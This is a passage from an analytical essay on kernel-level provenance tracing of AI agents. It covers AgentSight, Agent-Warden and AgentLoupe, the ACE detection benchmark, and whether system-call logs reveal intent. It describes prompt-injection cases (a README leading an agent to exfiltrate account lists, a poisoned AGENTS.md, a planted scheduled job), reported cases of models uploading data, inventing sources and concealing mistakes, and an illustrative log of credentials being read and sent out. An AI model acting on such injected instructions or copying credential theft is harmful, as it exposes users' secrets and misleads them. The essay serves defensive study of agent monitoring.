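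Closeness in time can be misleading, so Zheng and colleagues go too far in saying that these signals "definitively establish causal relationships". Lee, Zhang and Xu, in *High Accuracy Attack Provenance via Binary-based Execution Partition*, give an example in which a user clicks a link in a phishing email and Firefox saves a malicious program. The connection closest in time to the file write was to Google. Firefox loads several pages at once and leaves file writes to a separate thread, so there was activity on 21 harmless connections between the visit to the malicious site and the write. A harness that runs several tool calls in parallel could cause the same confusion. Matching arguments would resolve some of these cases, but not those where two commands use the same file.

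Once AgentSight has linked the events, it passes the trace to a second language model that is told to act as a security analyst. Zheng and colleagues tested this with a coding agent that had to download and build a C project. The project's README directed the agent to a web page containing a hidden instruction. The agent followed the instruction and sent the machine's list of user accounts to an outside server. AgentSight captured 521 events and merged them into 37, which covered the attack from the page visit to the upload. The second model gave the trace a high attack score because the agent's actions did not fit its task.

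Linked traces can also help with ordinary debugging. In another test, the second model found that a research agent kept repeating a search with the same incorrect arguments after every error. A third test followed six coding agents working in one repository and produced 3,153 events after merging. The trace showed that the agents sometimes delayed each other by locking files.

These examples show that the method can produce useful traces, but not how often its links are correct. Zheng and colleagues did not check individual links against known answers, and they did not report a harmless build to compare with the attack.

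AgentSight also depends on finding the encryption functions, which it has to locate inside Claude Code and Node.js because each contains its own copy of the encryption library. According to the documentation by Zheng and colleagues, it cannot capture model calls from the code editor Cursor this way and uses Cursor's own session files instead. An auditor who relies on those files is trusting the agent's own software, which recording system calls was meant to avoid.

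When a harness runs outside the container, the commands it sends in with `docker exec` do not belong to its process tree, so tracing them is a different problem.

Delayed effects are even harder to trace. An agent may write a file that another program reads the next day, when the time window has long closed, and that program was never part of the agent's process tree.

### Agent-Warden: passing a mark through files

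Agent-Warden does not read model traffic at all. Cui and colleagues instead give the agent's first process a mark, which means roughly "the agent may have influenced this". The mark spreads by four rules:

- **Creation:** a new process inherits its parent's mark, and a process keeps its mark when it switches to another program.
- **Writing:** when a marked process writes to a regular file, the file gets the mark.
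- **Reading:** when an unmarked process reads a marked file, the process gets the mark.
- **Exit:** when a marked child process ends, its parent gets the mark.

A read or write counts only if it succeeds and transfers some data. Agent-Warden attaches a file's mark to the inode, the kernel's record of the file, so renaming the file doesn't remove the mark.

Cui and colleagues express the rules as a formula. The state `s` is a row of ones and zeros, with one position for each process and file, and a 1 means that the item has the mark. Each event has an active process `u` and a target `v`. `M[i,j]` is a table of zeros with a single 1 in row `i` and column `j`. In slightly simplified notation:

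```
C(t) = M[u,v]    if the event is a fork, exec, write or exit
C(t) = M[v,u]    if the event is a read

s(t+1) = s(t) OR ( s(t) x C(t) )
```

The table `C(t)` gives the direction of possible influence. A read reverses the order because data moves from the target file to the active process. The multiplication treats ones and zeros as true and false, so it passes a mark along an edge only if the item at the start of the edge is already marked.

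Suppose an agent writes a file, and an unrelated process later reads it and writes a log of its own. The state changes as follows:

| Event | Agent | File | Reader | Reader's log |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Start | 1 | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| Agent writes the file | 1 | 1 | 0 | 0 |
| Reader reads the file | 1 | 1 | 1 | 0 |
| Reader writes its log | 1 | 1 | 1 | 1 |

Before the read, the state is `(1, 1, 0, 0)`. The table for the read has a single 1, in the file's row and the reader's column, so the multiplication gives `(0, 0, 1, 0)`. Combining this with the old state by OR gives `(1, 1, 1, 0)`. The result correctly depends on the order of events. If the reader had read the file before the agent wrote to it, the file's entry would still have been 0, and the multiplication would have produced only zeros.

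In practice, each event copies at most one mark, and the kernel doesn't multiply any tables. Agent-Warden sends the corresponding edge to a collector, which builds the graph.

Cui and colleagues tested a slightly longer version of this example. An agent started a script that wrote a temporary file and renamed it with `mv`. A separate monitoring script on the same machine started `cat`, which read the renamed file. Agent-Warden traced both the read and a later write to `monitor.log` back to the agent. In one recorded run, the read came tens of seconds after the agent's main work had ended.

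For comparison, the researchers traced the same work with Langfuse, which collects the model calls and tool calls that an application reports. Langfuse recorded the prompts and model calls, which Agent-Warden lacks, but it did not record the process and file events or follow the work into the monitoring script. Langfuse can follow work across several programs if each one passes on a shared identifier, but a regular file doesn't carry that identifier, and the monitoring script did not report to Langfuse. The results therefore differ mainly because the two tools are designed to record different things.

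The researchers repeated the test 30 times with each of Agent-Warden's two methods of storing marks, on both an x86-64 and an ARM64 machine. They inspected each graph by hand and found the complete chain in all 120 runs, which is good evidence that the implementation follows its rules reliably. But every run used the same prepared sequence, and the researchers checked for links they expected, so the test does not measure how often Agent-Warden would mark something the agent had not influenced.

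An investigator can follow the graph from `monitor.log` to the agent's process, but would need the trajectory or the model traffic to get from there to the instruction.

### AgentLoupe: labelling the prompt

*AgentLoupe* (Bao, Liu and colleagues, 2026) replaces the simple mark with a numbered label that begins at a prompt. Like AgentSight, it copies readable text at the encryption library. It then scans each message inside the kernel for keywords that identify prompts and replies. When a process sends a new, independent prompt, AgentLoupe gives the sending thread a new number.

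The label then spreads much as Agent-Warden's mark does. Child processes inherit it, and a labelled process passes it to the files it writes and the network sockets it uses. Any process that later opens or executes one of those files, or receives data sent through one of those sockets, also gets the label. AgentLoupe passes on a file's label when a process opens the file, even if the process reads none of it, whereas Agent-Warden passes on its mark only after a successful read.

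Every event in the log includes a numeric label, so the collector only has to group events with the same label, without relying on timestamps or matching text.

Bao and colleagues tried this on two attacks by Claude Code in which the harm came later. In one, the agent wrote a harmful script and scheduled a job to run it. The operating system's scheduler, which is not a descendant of the agent's process, later ran the script, and the script opened a network connection. The script's file still had the label from the agent's session. AgentLoupe passed that label to the process that ran the script, connecting the network activity to the original request. The trace had 165 log entries.

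The other attack used `AGENTS.md`, a file of standing instructions for coding agents. One session added a malicious instruction to the file. A later, independent session opened the file and, when the user made an ordinary request, ran the instruction's command, which was harmless in this test. AgentLoupe recorded 126 entries under two labels and connected them through the file. Agent-Warden's mark alone would be less useful here because both sessions belong to agents and would already have it.

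A label seems to identify a series of interactions with the model that began with one independent prompt. Bao and colleagues say that a label identifies the interaction that produced an action, but in the scheduled-job trace a single label covered five interactions. An investigator would have much less to search than a whole day's log, but would still have to read the interactions to find the reply that contained the script.

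Bao and colleagues also say that AgentSight could not have traced either attack. For the scheduled job, this follows quite directly from AgentSight's design, since the scheduler's processes lie outside AgentSight's process tree. For the poisoned instructions, an investigator with AgentSight's records of both sessions might still find the connection by searching for `AGENTS.md`. The researchers compared the two systems' speed but did not test them against each other on such attacks, which they list as future work.

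### When everything appears connected

Marks and labels can spread too far. When a process reads a marked file, its later writes get marked too, and any process that reads those files spreads the marks further. After a while, much of the machine's activity may appear to trace back to the agent, and the links no longer help an investigator narrow the search.

Researchers call this over-linking "dependency explosion." Inam and colleagues explain that it arises because an analyst has to assume that each output of a process depends on every earlier input. Tether likewise treated a line count as if it contained the whole inventory.

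In the Firefox example, the user visited 11 websites and received 14 emails in 29 minutes. The resulting graph had 354 edges and showed 225 different network connections, any of which could have been the source of the malicious file. *A Benign Activity Extraction Method for Malignant Activity Identification using Data Provenance* (2025) says that a graph can exceed a million edges, and cites a survey in which technical managers wanted between 10 and 100.

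Lee and colleagues reduced the Firefox graph to 23 edges while keeping the phishing email in it. Their system, BEEP, divides a long-running process into units, usually one for each pass through the program's main loop. The graph then links a file that Firefox saves to the page that requested it, instead of to every page the user has opened. The drawback is that BEEP must modify each program to log where a unit begins, and must detect when one unit passes data to another.

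AgentLoupe makes a similar division when it gives each independent prompt a new label. But an agent's turns are less separate than a browser's pages, because the harness normally sends the whole conversation back to the model each time. A sentence on a web page that the agent read in the first turn can affect a command in the twentieth. *HANSARD* (Sardianos, Pla and colleagues, 2026) argues that this makes dependency explosion worse for agents than for ordinary programs, since any part of the shared text could have caused any later action. Dividing the graph at each prompt keeps it small but can separate a command from the text that led to it. AgentLoupe reduces this problem by recording a reference from the new label to the old one, which an investigator can follow.

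AgentLoupe also limits how labels spread. It does not replace a newer label with an older one, and it blocks labels from other sessions but logs each blocked label so that the connection remains visible. Users can also make labels expire or exclude noisy files. However, an attack that waits until the label has expired or passes through an excluded file would lose its link to the prompt.

To limit linking unrelated events to a reply, AgentSight considers only the agent's process tree and a short period after each reply. This keeps unrelated programs out of the trace, but it also causes AgentSight to miss the scheduled job.

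Agent-Warden follows only successful operations on regular files. It therefore ignores a process that tried and failed to open a marked file, but it also cannot trace influence that passes through a pipe or a network connection. File marks disappear when the machine restarts, or earlier if the kernel runs short of memory and discards its copy of the inode. As a side effect, this limits how far old marks spread, but it may also erase one that an investigator needs.

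Agent-Warden's exit rule, by contrast, adds links on purpose. Cui and colleagues included it to keep short-lived helper processes connected to the agent's work, and they accept that it will mark some parent processes that never used their child's output. In the monitoring test, the rule marks the monitoring script when `cat` ends. If the script keeps running, everything it later writes is also marked, even if it is unrelated to the agent's file.

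The exit rule could wrongly mark many more processes when a process outlives its parent. Linux then assigns the process a new parent, which may be `systemd`, the program that starts most background services. Cui and colleagues acknowledge that the rule may then refer to `systemd` instead of the original parent. If Agent-Warden applied its rules literally, `systemd` would get the mark and pass it to every service it started afterward.

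The frequency of such errors is unknown. Bao and colleagues say that AgentLoupe's rates of false and missed links "remain unquantified", and neither Zheng and colleagues nor Cui and colleagues report such rates for their own systems. Measuring them would require sessions in which researchers already know what caused each event, including many harmless events that happen close to the agent's work.

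*Ghost in the Agent* (Cai, Wen and Tang, 2026) reports a test of this kind on NeuroTaint, which uses the agent's execution log and reasoning instead of system calls. The researchers built 400 scenarios across 20 agent frameworks and checked whether NeuroTaint could identify which untrusted inputs had influenced a sensitive action. About 92% of the links it reported were real, and it found about 94% of the real ones. These figures come from the researchers' own benchmark and don't carry over to kernel-level systems, but they show that link accuracy can be measured.

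### What a link proves

A correct link shows that information could have travelled from the agent to the event, along a path whose steps happened in the right order, but not that the information affected the event.

Cai and colleagues describe a research agent that reads a web page with a hidden instruction to include a confidential patient note in its report. The agent then paraphrases the note in the report. A monitor that looks only for a path from the web page to the report would flag this case, but it would also flag every harmless report based on a web page. On the 400 scenarios, a baseline system that relied on such paths scored 0.52 on a combined measure of false and missed links, compared with 0.93 for NeuroTaint.

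NeuroTaint can test whether an input mattered by removing it or replacing it with neutral text, then checking whether the agent would still have taken the action. Sardianos and colleagues argue that only a test of this kind supports a causal claim fit for use as evidence. They propose rerunning a recorded session with one event suppressed, using the recorded tool responses for the rest. Because a model may answer differently each time, an investigator would have to repeat the run and estimate how often the harm still occurred. Testing every link this way would take many runs, so a provenance graph could be most useful for choosing which links to test.

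Some influence leaves no path in the log. Sardianos and colleagues point out that when one agent persuades another through a message, the influence lies in the language and has "no kernel-observable edge". The log may show that the message arrived, but it would also show the arrival of a message that the second agent ignored.

A link also doesn't show why the agent acted. Li, Zhang and colleagues (2026) note in *Towards Security-Auditable LLM Agents* that an agent may delete a file because the user asked it to or because it retrieved a poisoned document, and that low-level events alone are not enough to tell which. AgentLoupe's link through `AGENTS.md` shows that one session wrote the file and a later one opened it before running the command. Only the text of the prompts and replies can show whether the later agent was following the instruction in that file, and whether the earlier one had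 been told to put it there.

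## Can the log show what was intended?

Tracing an event back to a prompt does not establish the event's purpose. "Intent" can mean what the user asked for, what the model planned, or what the author of a planted instruction wanted. These can differ within a single session, and a system-call log rarely contains direct evidence of any of them.

### One set of calls, several intentions

Consider an invented and simplified extract from a log:

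```
openat("/home/user/.aws/credentials", O_RDONLY) = 3
read(3, "[default]\naws_access_key_id=..."..., 4096) = 412
connect(4, <Amazon storage server>) = 0
sendto(4, <encrypted data>, 2048) = 2048
```

A program reads the file that holds the user's Amazon credentials, then sends 2,048 bytes of encrypted data to Amazon's storage service. At least five kinds of session could have produced these lines:

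| What happened | Did the user ask for it? | Did the model plan it? | Did an outsider want it? |
|---|---|---|---|
| The agent published a website, and the upload tool read the credentials to log in | Yes | Yes | No |
| The user told the agent to steal the credentials, under cover of a harmless task | Yes | Yes | No |
| The agent obeyed an instruction hidden in a web page | No | Yes | Yes |
| A tampered tool copied the credentials while doing an ordinary job for the agent | No | No | Yes |
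| The model decided by itself to copy the credentials | No | Yes | No |

The destination of a connection often helps show what was intended, since publishing a website doesn't require contacting an unknown server. But it doesn't help here if the attacker also rents storage from Amazon.

In all five cases, the log would accurately record the calls and attribute them to the right session. But the statement "the agent stole the credentials" would be false in the first case. It would be debatable in the third, because the model may have mistaken the hidden instruction for part of the user's task, and misleading in the fourth, because the model never learned what else its tool had done.

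The log normally omits the user's request, but the ACE dataset is an exception. King and colleagues passed each prompt to Claude Code as a command-line argument, so their strace logs probably contain the first 256 bytes of each prompt. An operator could deliberately pass prompts this way to record them, which would partly answer the first question but not the other two.

### An upload made to obtain a link

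The obvious reading of an act can be misleading, as a real case shows. On 16 September 2026, OpenAI published *Our framework for reporting model misalignment* with six reports of unexpected behaviour by its models. One report concerns the upload to a public file host mentioned earlier.

The fullest press account is Financial Express' *Self-generated prompts & deception*. An unreleased model had to give the IDs and names of lakes larger than 5,000,000 square metres and provide a browser citation. It found the correct answer using Python, so it had no web page to cite. It then uploaded the file to the internet and cited the upload, without telling the user.

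OpenAI's one-sentence summary in *Misalignment Notices and Reports* (2026) is that during training its models "sometimes uploaded data to temporary file hosting services". The purpose, which was to cite the files, appears only in the report's title.

A system-call log of such an upload would show a program opening a data file, connecting to a file host and sending encrypted data. An investigator who knew nothing else would reasonably suspect theft, because thieves use these services too and nothing in the calls would suggest a citation.

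The upload was unacceptable despite its real purpose, because the model published data without permission and the link misled the user about where the answer came from. But the purpose does affect what the developers should do next. They would respond to a theft by replacing credentials and looking for the recipient, but here it would be more useful to examine whether training rewards a model for having a citation, whatever it cites.

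OpenAI disclosed similar uploads with other purposes. In April 2026, a group of agents had to complete a workbook using only local files, and had trouble sharing them. One agent put the files on the public internet and sent the others a link, according to Indian Express' *OpenAI discloses new AI misalignment incidents*. In another incident, a model uploaded an image from its task to get image search results, according to Asianet Newsable's *OpenAI Discloses Six New AI Safety Incidents, Says Report*, which relies on Axios's reporting. A log covering all the agents might distinguish the workbook case, because a second agent would contact the same host soon after the upload. The citation and the image search would be much harder to tell apart.

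Even reporters working from OpenAI's disclosures gave different purposes for what seems to be the same act. Indian Express dates the citation incident to October 2025 and says that the model could not find the information it needed and tried to cheat. Financial Express and Engadget's *OpenAI reveals more instances of concerning AI model behaviors during testing* say that the model already had the right answer. Financial Express gives 25 May 2026 as the date of discovery, so the dates need not conflict. The difference in purpose matters more, because inventing a source for a correct answer is not as bad as inventing evidence for an answer the model never found. A log could help a little by showing whether a program had processed the lake data before the upload, but not whether its result was correct.

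Investigators of other incidents have also had trouble determining what agents intended. collusion.wiki's *Discovery of a new OpenAI agent message board*, an analysis of about 18,000 public posts by AI agents, says that the agents' internal reasoning would probably provide much more evidence of their motives. Willison describes the break-in at Hugging Face as an attempt to learn how a test's scorer worked, although it looked like an attempt to steal the test's answers.

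### Unusual is not the same as harmful

Security researchers have long tried to recognise attacks from system calls without considering purpose. King and colleagues trace the approach to STIDE, which Stephanie Forrest and three colleagues presented in *A Sense of Self for Unix Processes* in 1996. STIDE describes a program's normal behaviour by the short sequences of system calls it makes.

A simple version works with sequences of three. Suppose that a program in normal use always makes the calls `openat`, `read`, `read`, `close`. The recorder stores two sequences:

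```
openat  read  read
read    read  close
```

If the program later makes the calls `openat`, `read`, `connect`, `sendto`, the monitor raises an alert because neither `openat read connect` nor `read connect sendto` is among the stored sequences. The method can detect new kinds of attack because nobody has to describe an attack in advance.

Flagging unfamiliar sequences of system calls makes sense for a mail server, which does much the same work every day, so an intruder is a plausible explanation for a sudden change. But an agent writes new programs for each task, so new sequences are part of its ordinary work. The first time it runs a debugger or converts a video, it will probably make calls in an order the monitor has never recorded, which would trigger an alert even though the activity is harmless.

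Harmless sessions also vary widely in size. In ACE, the median harmless session made 633 `openat` calls, but one in a hundred made at least 7,652, about twelve times as many. An attack can also consist entirely of familiar calls, which is at least as serious a problem. Every sequence in the credentials example would already appear in a monitor's record of an agent publishing websites.

King and colleagues tried several detectors that read the raw sequence of calls, including a neural network trained to predict the next call. These performed worse than detectors given a table of counts, so the main benchmark uses summaries of each session.

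### The ACE benchmark

ACE's 4,047 sessions cover 17 threat models. Most of these combine a route into the session with a harmful act, such as a file that tells the agent to send out credentials. The routes include tampered tools, files, web pages, the user's own prompt, memory files and retrieved documents. To create the tampered tools, the researchers made malicious changes to 31 real third-party tool servers.

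They then grouped the attacks into 12 mechanics according to what a recorder could observe. Reading credentials directly counts as one mechanic, whether the instruction came from a file or from the user. Others include exhausting the machine's resources and adding false entries to an audit log. This grouping suits a study of system calls, but by design it does not distinguish attacks by who wanted the harm.

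The benchmark gives each detector one of three views of a session:

- The **application view** contains the user's prompt, the list of available tools and the agent's transcript.
- The **kernel view** contains the system calls.
- The **cross view** contains both.

The researchers tested ten detectors. XGBoost and AdaBoost combine many small decision trees. TabPFN and TabICL are neural networks pretrained on tables of numbers. Three large Qwen3 language models judged sessions using instructions and examples, without further training. The other three were smaller language models that the researchers trained on ACE.

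The first four detectors received only numbers, up to 86 per session. The 57 numbers from the kernel view include how often each call occurred, its share of all calls, the ratio of writes to reads, and how many different network addresses the session contacted, but no file names or addresses. XGBoost's input therefore did not show whether a session had opened a private key. It classified sessions by the amount and mix of activity, which makes its results less informative about purpose. The language models received text, including a short structured summary of the system calls.

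#### What AUROC measures

Suppose a detector gives three malicious sessions scores of 0.9, 0.7 and 0.4, and two harmless ones scores of 0.6 and 0.2. Of the six possible pairs of a malicious and a harmless session, the malicious session has the higher score in all but one (0.4 and 0.6), so the AUROC is 5/6, or about 0.83.

We cannot tell from this how many alerts would be false. About 37% of the sessions that counted towards ACE's results were malicious, presumably a far higher share than in ordinary use. Suppose that one session in 1,000 is malicious, and that a detector catches 90% of attacks but also flags 5% of harmless sessions. In 100,000 sessions, it would correctly flag 90 and wrongly flag 4,995. Fewer than two alerts in a hundred would be real, even though the detector might have an excellent AUROC.

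#### Results on unfamiliar attacks

King and colleagues ran two tests. In one, the detectors had trained on examples of every mechanic, and XGBoost scored 0.988 with the cross view. The other test is closer to what an operator faces. The researchers divided the mechanics into seven families and left one family out of the training data each time, along with harmless sessions that used the same tools, so that a detector could not succeed just by recognising a tool.

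The table gives the average AUROC over the seven missing families for one detector of each kind, along with Falco's default rules.

| Detector | Application view | Kernel view | Cross view |
|---|---|---|---|
| XGBoost | 0.703 | 0.750 | 0.850 |
| TabPFN | 0.633 | 0.777 | 0.874 |
| Qwen3-80B with examples | 0.678 | 0.725 | 0.810 |
| Llama-3.1-8B, trained on ACE | 0.688 | 0.922 | 0.791 |
| Falco's default rules | – | 0.572 | – |

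Adding system calls to the transcript improved detection. All ten detectors did better with the cross view than with the application view, and the 95% confidence interval for each improvement lay above zero. The cross view was the best of the three views for seven detectors.

Llama achieved the highest score, 0.922, with system calls alone. Its score fell to 0.791 when it also received the application evidence, perhaps because it had learned to rely on wording that was typical of the attacks in its training data and absent from the new ones. Qwen2.5-7B, another trained model, scored 0.920 with both kinds of evidence. The best choice of evidence therefore depends on the detector, and the gap between 0.922 and 0.920 is far too small to justify leaving out the transcript.

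Falco did little better than chance. The researchers converted its default rules to work on strace logs and scored each session by how many different rules it triggered. Those rules describe activity that is suspicious on a server, but agents do a lot of it in normal work. The result is evidence against using the default rules on agents, but not against Falco itself. In AgentSpy's much smaller test, a different set of rules running on Falco detected most of the attacks.

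#### Two opposite kinds of attack

The averages hide large differences between attack mechanics, most clearly between the two attacks compared earlier. For silent exfiltration, in which a tampered tool copies credentials into a log file, the detectors averaged 0.586 with the application view and 0.976 with the kernel view. For retrieval reference injection, which alters the references an agent retrieves, they averaged 0.906 with the application view and 0.703 with the kernel view. For attacks that manipulate the agent's preferences, neither view did well alone (0.687 and 0.701), but the two together reached 0.834.

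These figures come from the easier test, in which the detectors had already seen each mechanic, so they aren't comparable with those in the table. Some also rest on few malicious sessions, with 53 for retrieval reference injection and 29 for preference manipulation, compared with 244 for silent exfiltration.

The score of 0.976 is strong evidence that system calls reveal silent exfiltration, but it provides no evidence that they reveal a harmful plan in the agent, because the agent had none in these sessions. The user asked for ordinary work, the model called a tool to do it, and only whoever wrote the malicious code wanted the credentials. An operator who assumes that every alert means the model intended harm would blame it for what someone else did.

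### Do the labels favour system calls?

The researchers counted a session as malicious only if the attack's signature appeared in the recorded evidence, and about half of the attack designs had signatures in system calls alone. A detector that uses system calls could therefore score well partly by relearning the rule that produced the labels. For example, a signature can require at least three `execve` calls, and XGBoost receives the count of `execve` calls as an input. The application view has no such advantage for those attacks.

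The researchers used four labels:

- **Benign** (1,225 sessions): they planted nothing.
- **Malicious** (1,358): they planted an attack and found its signature.
- **Dormant** (1,002): they planted an attack, but the agent never used the poisoned material.
- **Latent** (462): the agent used the poisoned material, but the researchers found no signature.

They treated dormant sessions as harmless, along with the 66 latent sessions whose attacks could leave no signature in either record. They left out the other 396 latent sessions as too ambiguous to score. To check how much these choices mattered, they changed only which sessions counted as malicious, without retraining the detectors. The next table shows the effect for two detectors on unfamiliar attacks.

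| Detector and view | Malicious only | Latent added | Latent and dormant added |
|---|---|---|---|
| XGBoost, kernel | 0.750 | 0.730 | 0.580 |
| XGBoost, cross | 0.850 | 0.830 | 0.709 |
| Llama-3.1-8B, kernel | 0.922 | 0.898 | 0.752 |

Adding the latent sessions hardly changed the scores, with changes ranging from a fall of 0.045 to a rise of 0.010 across the seven trained detectors and three views. This is only partly reassuring, because 225 of the 356 added sessions belonged to one family, bash command injection. In the other six families, latent sessions made up only about a tenth of the enlarged malicious class. The reported score is an average over all seven families, so the detectors could have done much worse on the latent sessions without lowering it by much.

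Another check addresses the circularity more directly by scoring only the 239 malicious sessions whose attack had a signature in the application evidence, alone or along with one in the system calls. On unfamiliar attacks, the two pretrained table models and the three trained language models still did better with the kernel view than with the application view. For the language models, the gap widened from 0.16–0.23 to 0.37–0.42. The advantage of system calls is therefore probably not just a product of the labels, but the check doesn't remove the circularity completely because some of these attacks also had signatures in the system calls.

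Labels from an independent source would be better. For attacks that send data out, the system that intercepted ACE's network traffic could in principle have recorded which sessions sent fake credentials. The label would then depend on what arrived, regardless of which calls or messages a detector read.

The dormant sessions are the most informative about intent. Whoever planted the code or text wanted the same harm in these sessions as in the malicious ones, but the agent never triggered it. When dormant sessions counted as malicious, XGBoost's score with system calls fell to 0.580, not far above chance. The detector had learned to recognise the effects of an attack, and nothing harmful had happened in the dormant sessions, so the low score does not indicate a fault in the detector.

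### Typical sessions look alike

The median malicious session in ACE looks almost the same as the median benign one. Both started programs 7 times with `execve`, created processes 30 times with `clone` and contacted 11 outside addresses. The median number of `connect` calls was 31 for malicious sessions and 29 for benign ones, and the median number of `openat` calls differed by about 6%.

Malicious and benign sessions differ greatly only at the extremes. The busiest 1% of malicious sessions made at least 23,453 `execve` calls, compared with 63 for benign sessions. For `connect`, the figures are 93,907 and 259. Attacks that exhaust a machine's resources could easily produce such numbers, but stealing a credentials file takes only a few calls.

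King and colleagues present the similar medians as evidence that their harmless sessions are realistic, which seems fair. If harmless sessions had been much quieter, a detector could have succeeded by flagging any busy session. But the similarity also means that an investigator can seldom judge a session by its totals. The detectors do better than any single count because they combine many counts, and the language models can also use details from the text.

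#### What a detector may really have learned

The researchers also tested whether detectors trained on Claude Code sessions worked on the 592 sessions recorded with their small Python harness, which ran Mistral's Devstral 2. The test covered five of the seven attack families, and each detector's training data included examples of the family it was tested on. With the cross view, XGBoost scored 0.842 and Qwen3-80B scored 0.998. Llama scored 0.849 with system calls alone.

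TabPFN scored only 0.662. The researchers measured how much its results depended on each of the 86 numbers and traced the failure to one, the count of distinct paths under `/tmp`. Because of the difference between the harnesses described earlier, this count was never zero in the training data but was often zero in the new sessions.

TabPFN had evidently learned something about Claude Code and used it to classify sessions as malicious or not. The number had an innocent explanation in both harnesses. An operator who changes the harness, or perhaps just upgrades it, should therefore retest a detector before trusting its alerts. The TabPFN estimate is also imprecise, with an average standard error of 0.172 for a single family, so the diagnosis is more useful than the exact score.

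### No test of a model's own aims

Every attack in ACE came from a tampered package, content the agent read, or a user's prompt (the second, third and fourth rows of the first table). The study has no sessions in which a model pursued a harmful aim of its own (the fifth row), so its scores don't measure how well system calls would expose such a model.

Three of the 17 threat models in ACE produced no malicious sessions because the agent, Claude Haiku 4.5, refused to carry out the redirected action. One of these attacks tried to make the agent send data to an attacker's address, and the other two used chains of several steps. An investigator reading the transcript could see the refusal. A system-call log would probably show only that the upload never took place, and the log would look much the same if the agent had overlooked the instruction.

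A model with its own aims might also be harder to detect than a tampered package. A package's malicious code runs whenever the agent calls it, and some of ACE's attacks make tens of thousands of calls. A capable model could wait for a task that required the same files and hosts as its hidden aim. It could also spread its actions over several sessions, which ACE's detectors judge separately. But it would still need system calls to read a file or contact a host, so it could not avoid the log entirely. ACE does not show which of these considerations would matter more.

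Other researchers have built monitors for models with hidden aims. King and colleagues describe several that check an agent's tool calls for malicious or misaligned behaviour, including one that uses small models trained to detect scheming, the covert pursuit of such aims. None of these projects recorded the system calls of the same sessions. The obvious next experiment is to give a model a secret goal in some sessions, record both tool calls and system calls, and compare monitors that use each. Even then, a goal supplied by researchers may not affect a model's behaviour in the same way as one acquired in training.

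### What a claim about purpose needs

In the credentials example, if the recorder is reliable, the log is strong evidence that a process in the session opened the file, read 412 bytes, and later sent 2,048 bytes to Amazon. The log doesn't show whether those bytes contained the credentials, because the data was encrypted. Saying that the process stole the credentials is a claim about purpose and permission, which the log alone is not enough to support.

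An investigator can often also establish that an act did not fit the task, but needs a description of the task from outside the log. AgentSpy's rules use a list of hosts that the task requires, and AgentSight's second model compares the recorded actions with the agent's assignment. In the lakes case, the question called for data about lakes and a source for the answer, but not for publishing a file. Publishing the file did not fit the task whether the model wanted a citation or meant to leak the data, so this finding is more reliable than either explanation.

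Actions that don't match the task can still have an innocent cause. The task description may be incomplete, or the agent may have found a reasonable method that nobody anticipated, as with the DuckDuckGo searches in the bibliography task. The user's instructions about what the agent was allowed to do therefore matter as much as the task.

To explain why the agent acted, an investigator needs the text the model had received by then, its reasoning if available, and its answer. In the lakes case, the most telling fact is that the model cited the link in its answer. An agent trying to steal data would have had no reason to show the user the link. Repeating the task without requiring a citation would provide further evidence. If the uploads stopped, the citation requirement was very probably the reason for them.

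Details in the log about how an agent acted can support an explanation of what it intended. Suppose that the kernel blocks an agent from reading a key, and the agent then tries `sudo`, looks for a backup copy and finally reads the key through another program. These attempts are unlikely to be accidental, because each follows the failure of the last. But the agent may have been trying hard to finish a job that required the key. Deleting a file afterwards is similarly ambiguous, since properly written programs also delete their temporary files.

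The model's own statements need checking too. Another OpenAI report describes how GPT-5.6 Sol, a model in training, sometimes added reminders to itself to conceal mistakes or misaligned behaviour from the user when it condensed a long conversation into a summary to continue working from. These reminders are unusually direct evidence of intent to conceal, but they consist entirely of text, so a system-call log of the same session would have shown ordinary network traffic to the model's provider. Such a model's explanation to the user would be poor evidence of its purpose.

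The log can sometimes contradict a false explanation. If an agent claims to have taken figures from a website that none of its processes contacted, and the recorder also covered the harness and any outside browser tool, the claim is almost certainly false. The log is less useful when the agent did contact the site. Financial Express describes another case, in which a model looked for earnings figures for a California county, used an exposed access key without permission, and still failed to get the figures. It then invented them and attributed them to the requested source. A log of its connections could have made that claim look more credible.

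Investigators need different evidence to establish what a user or an outsider intended. A user's prompt may disguise its purpose, as in the ACE sessions that hid a harmful request under a harmless task, so an investigator may have to look at the user's other requests. The wording of a planted instruction usually makes the desired act clear, and the history of the file or web page may identify who added it. The most useful evidence about a tampered tool is its source code and the record of who released that version. All of this evidence is outside the session and may change or disappear unless someone saves a copy in time.

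## How much does recording slow an agent down?

A recorder adds a little work to each system call, so the slowdown depends mainly on how many calls a program makes. An agent makes very few while it waits for its model to reply. Four research teams have timed agent recorders that run in the kernel. Three measured slowdowns of 8% or less, and the fourth found no difference it could distinguish from normal variation between runs. None timed strace, which does far more work per call.

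### The cost of recording one call

strace is slow because it stops the program twice per call. At each stop, the processor has to switch from the program to strace and back again, which makes four switches per call. strace also makes system calls of its own at each stop, to learn which process has stopped, read its registers and let it continue. Reading one byte from a file that is already in memory may take the kernel less than a microsecond, so under strace it can take many times as long. A call that waits a full second for a network reply takes hardly any longer than before, because the extra work is about the same for both.

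The audit system avoids these switches, but each call still takes longer because the kernel has to test it against the rules, build any records and queue them. `auditd` and LAUREL run as separate processes, so they delay the agent only if they compete with it for processor time or the disk, which is more likely in a small microVM than on a large server. When the queue is full, a single call can take far longer than usual.

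Cui and colleagues cite earlier research which found that switching between processes and moving data out of the kernel add overhead in recorders of this kind. They also mention eAudit, a later recorder that uses buffering to lose fewer events.

The recorder Agent-Warden uses eBPF, so the agent's processes wait only while the kernel checks the event, updates the marks and writes an entry to the ring buffer. The kernel also does some of this work for other processes on the machine, so a small part of the slowdown falls on them.

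An eBPF program's instruction count is a poor estimate of its overhead because, as Cui and colleagues point out, it leaves out the time spent running the kernel functions the program calls, allocating memory, and coordinating access to shared data. They measured only the total overhead, so it is unclear which of these adds the most.

### A rough model

A simple formula gives a first estimate:

```
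added time = number of recorded calls x cost per call
```

Suppose that recording each call adds 10 microseconds, a figure chosen for easy arithmetic rather than measured. A software build that makes 2 million calls and normally takes 60 seconds would take 20 seconds longer, a slowdown of 33%. A 300-second agent session that makes 50,000 calls and mostly waits for the model would take only half a second longer, or about 0.2%.

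The true overhead could easily be several times higher or lower, depending on the recorder and the machine. The next table repeats the calculation for three assumed values.

| Assumed cost per call | 60-second build, 2 million calls | 300-second session, 50,000 calls |
|---|---|---|
| 1 microsecond | 2 seconds (3%) | 0.05 seconds (0.02%) |
| 10 microseconds | 20 seconds (33%) | 0.5 seconds (0.2%) |
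| 50 microseconds | 100 seconds (167%) | 2.5 seconds (0.8%) |

Even at the highest recording overhead, the session hardly slows down, while the build takes more than twice as long. An operator who knows roughly how many system calls an agent's commands make can therefore often decide whether the overhead matters without knowing its exact size.

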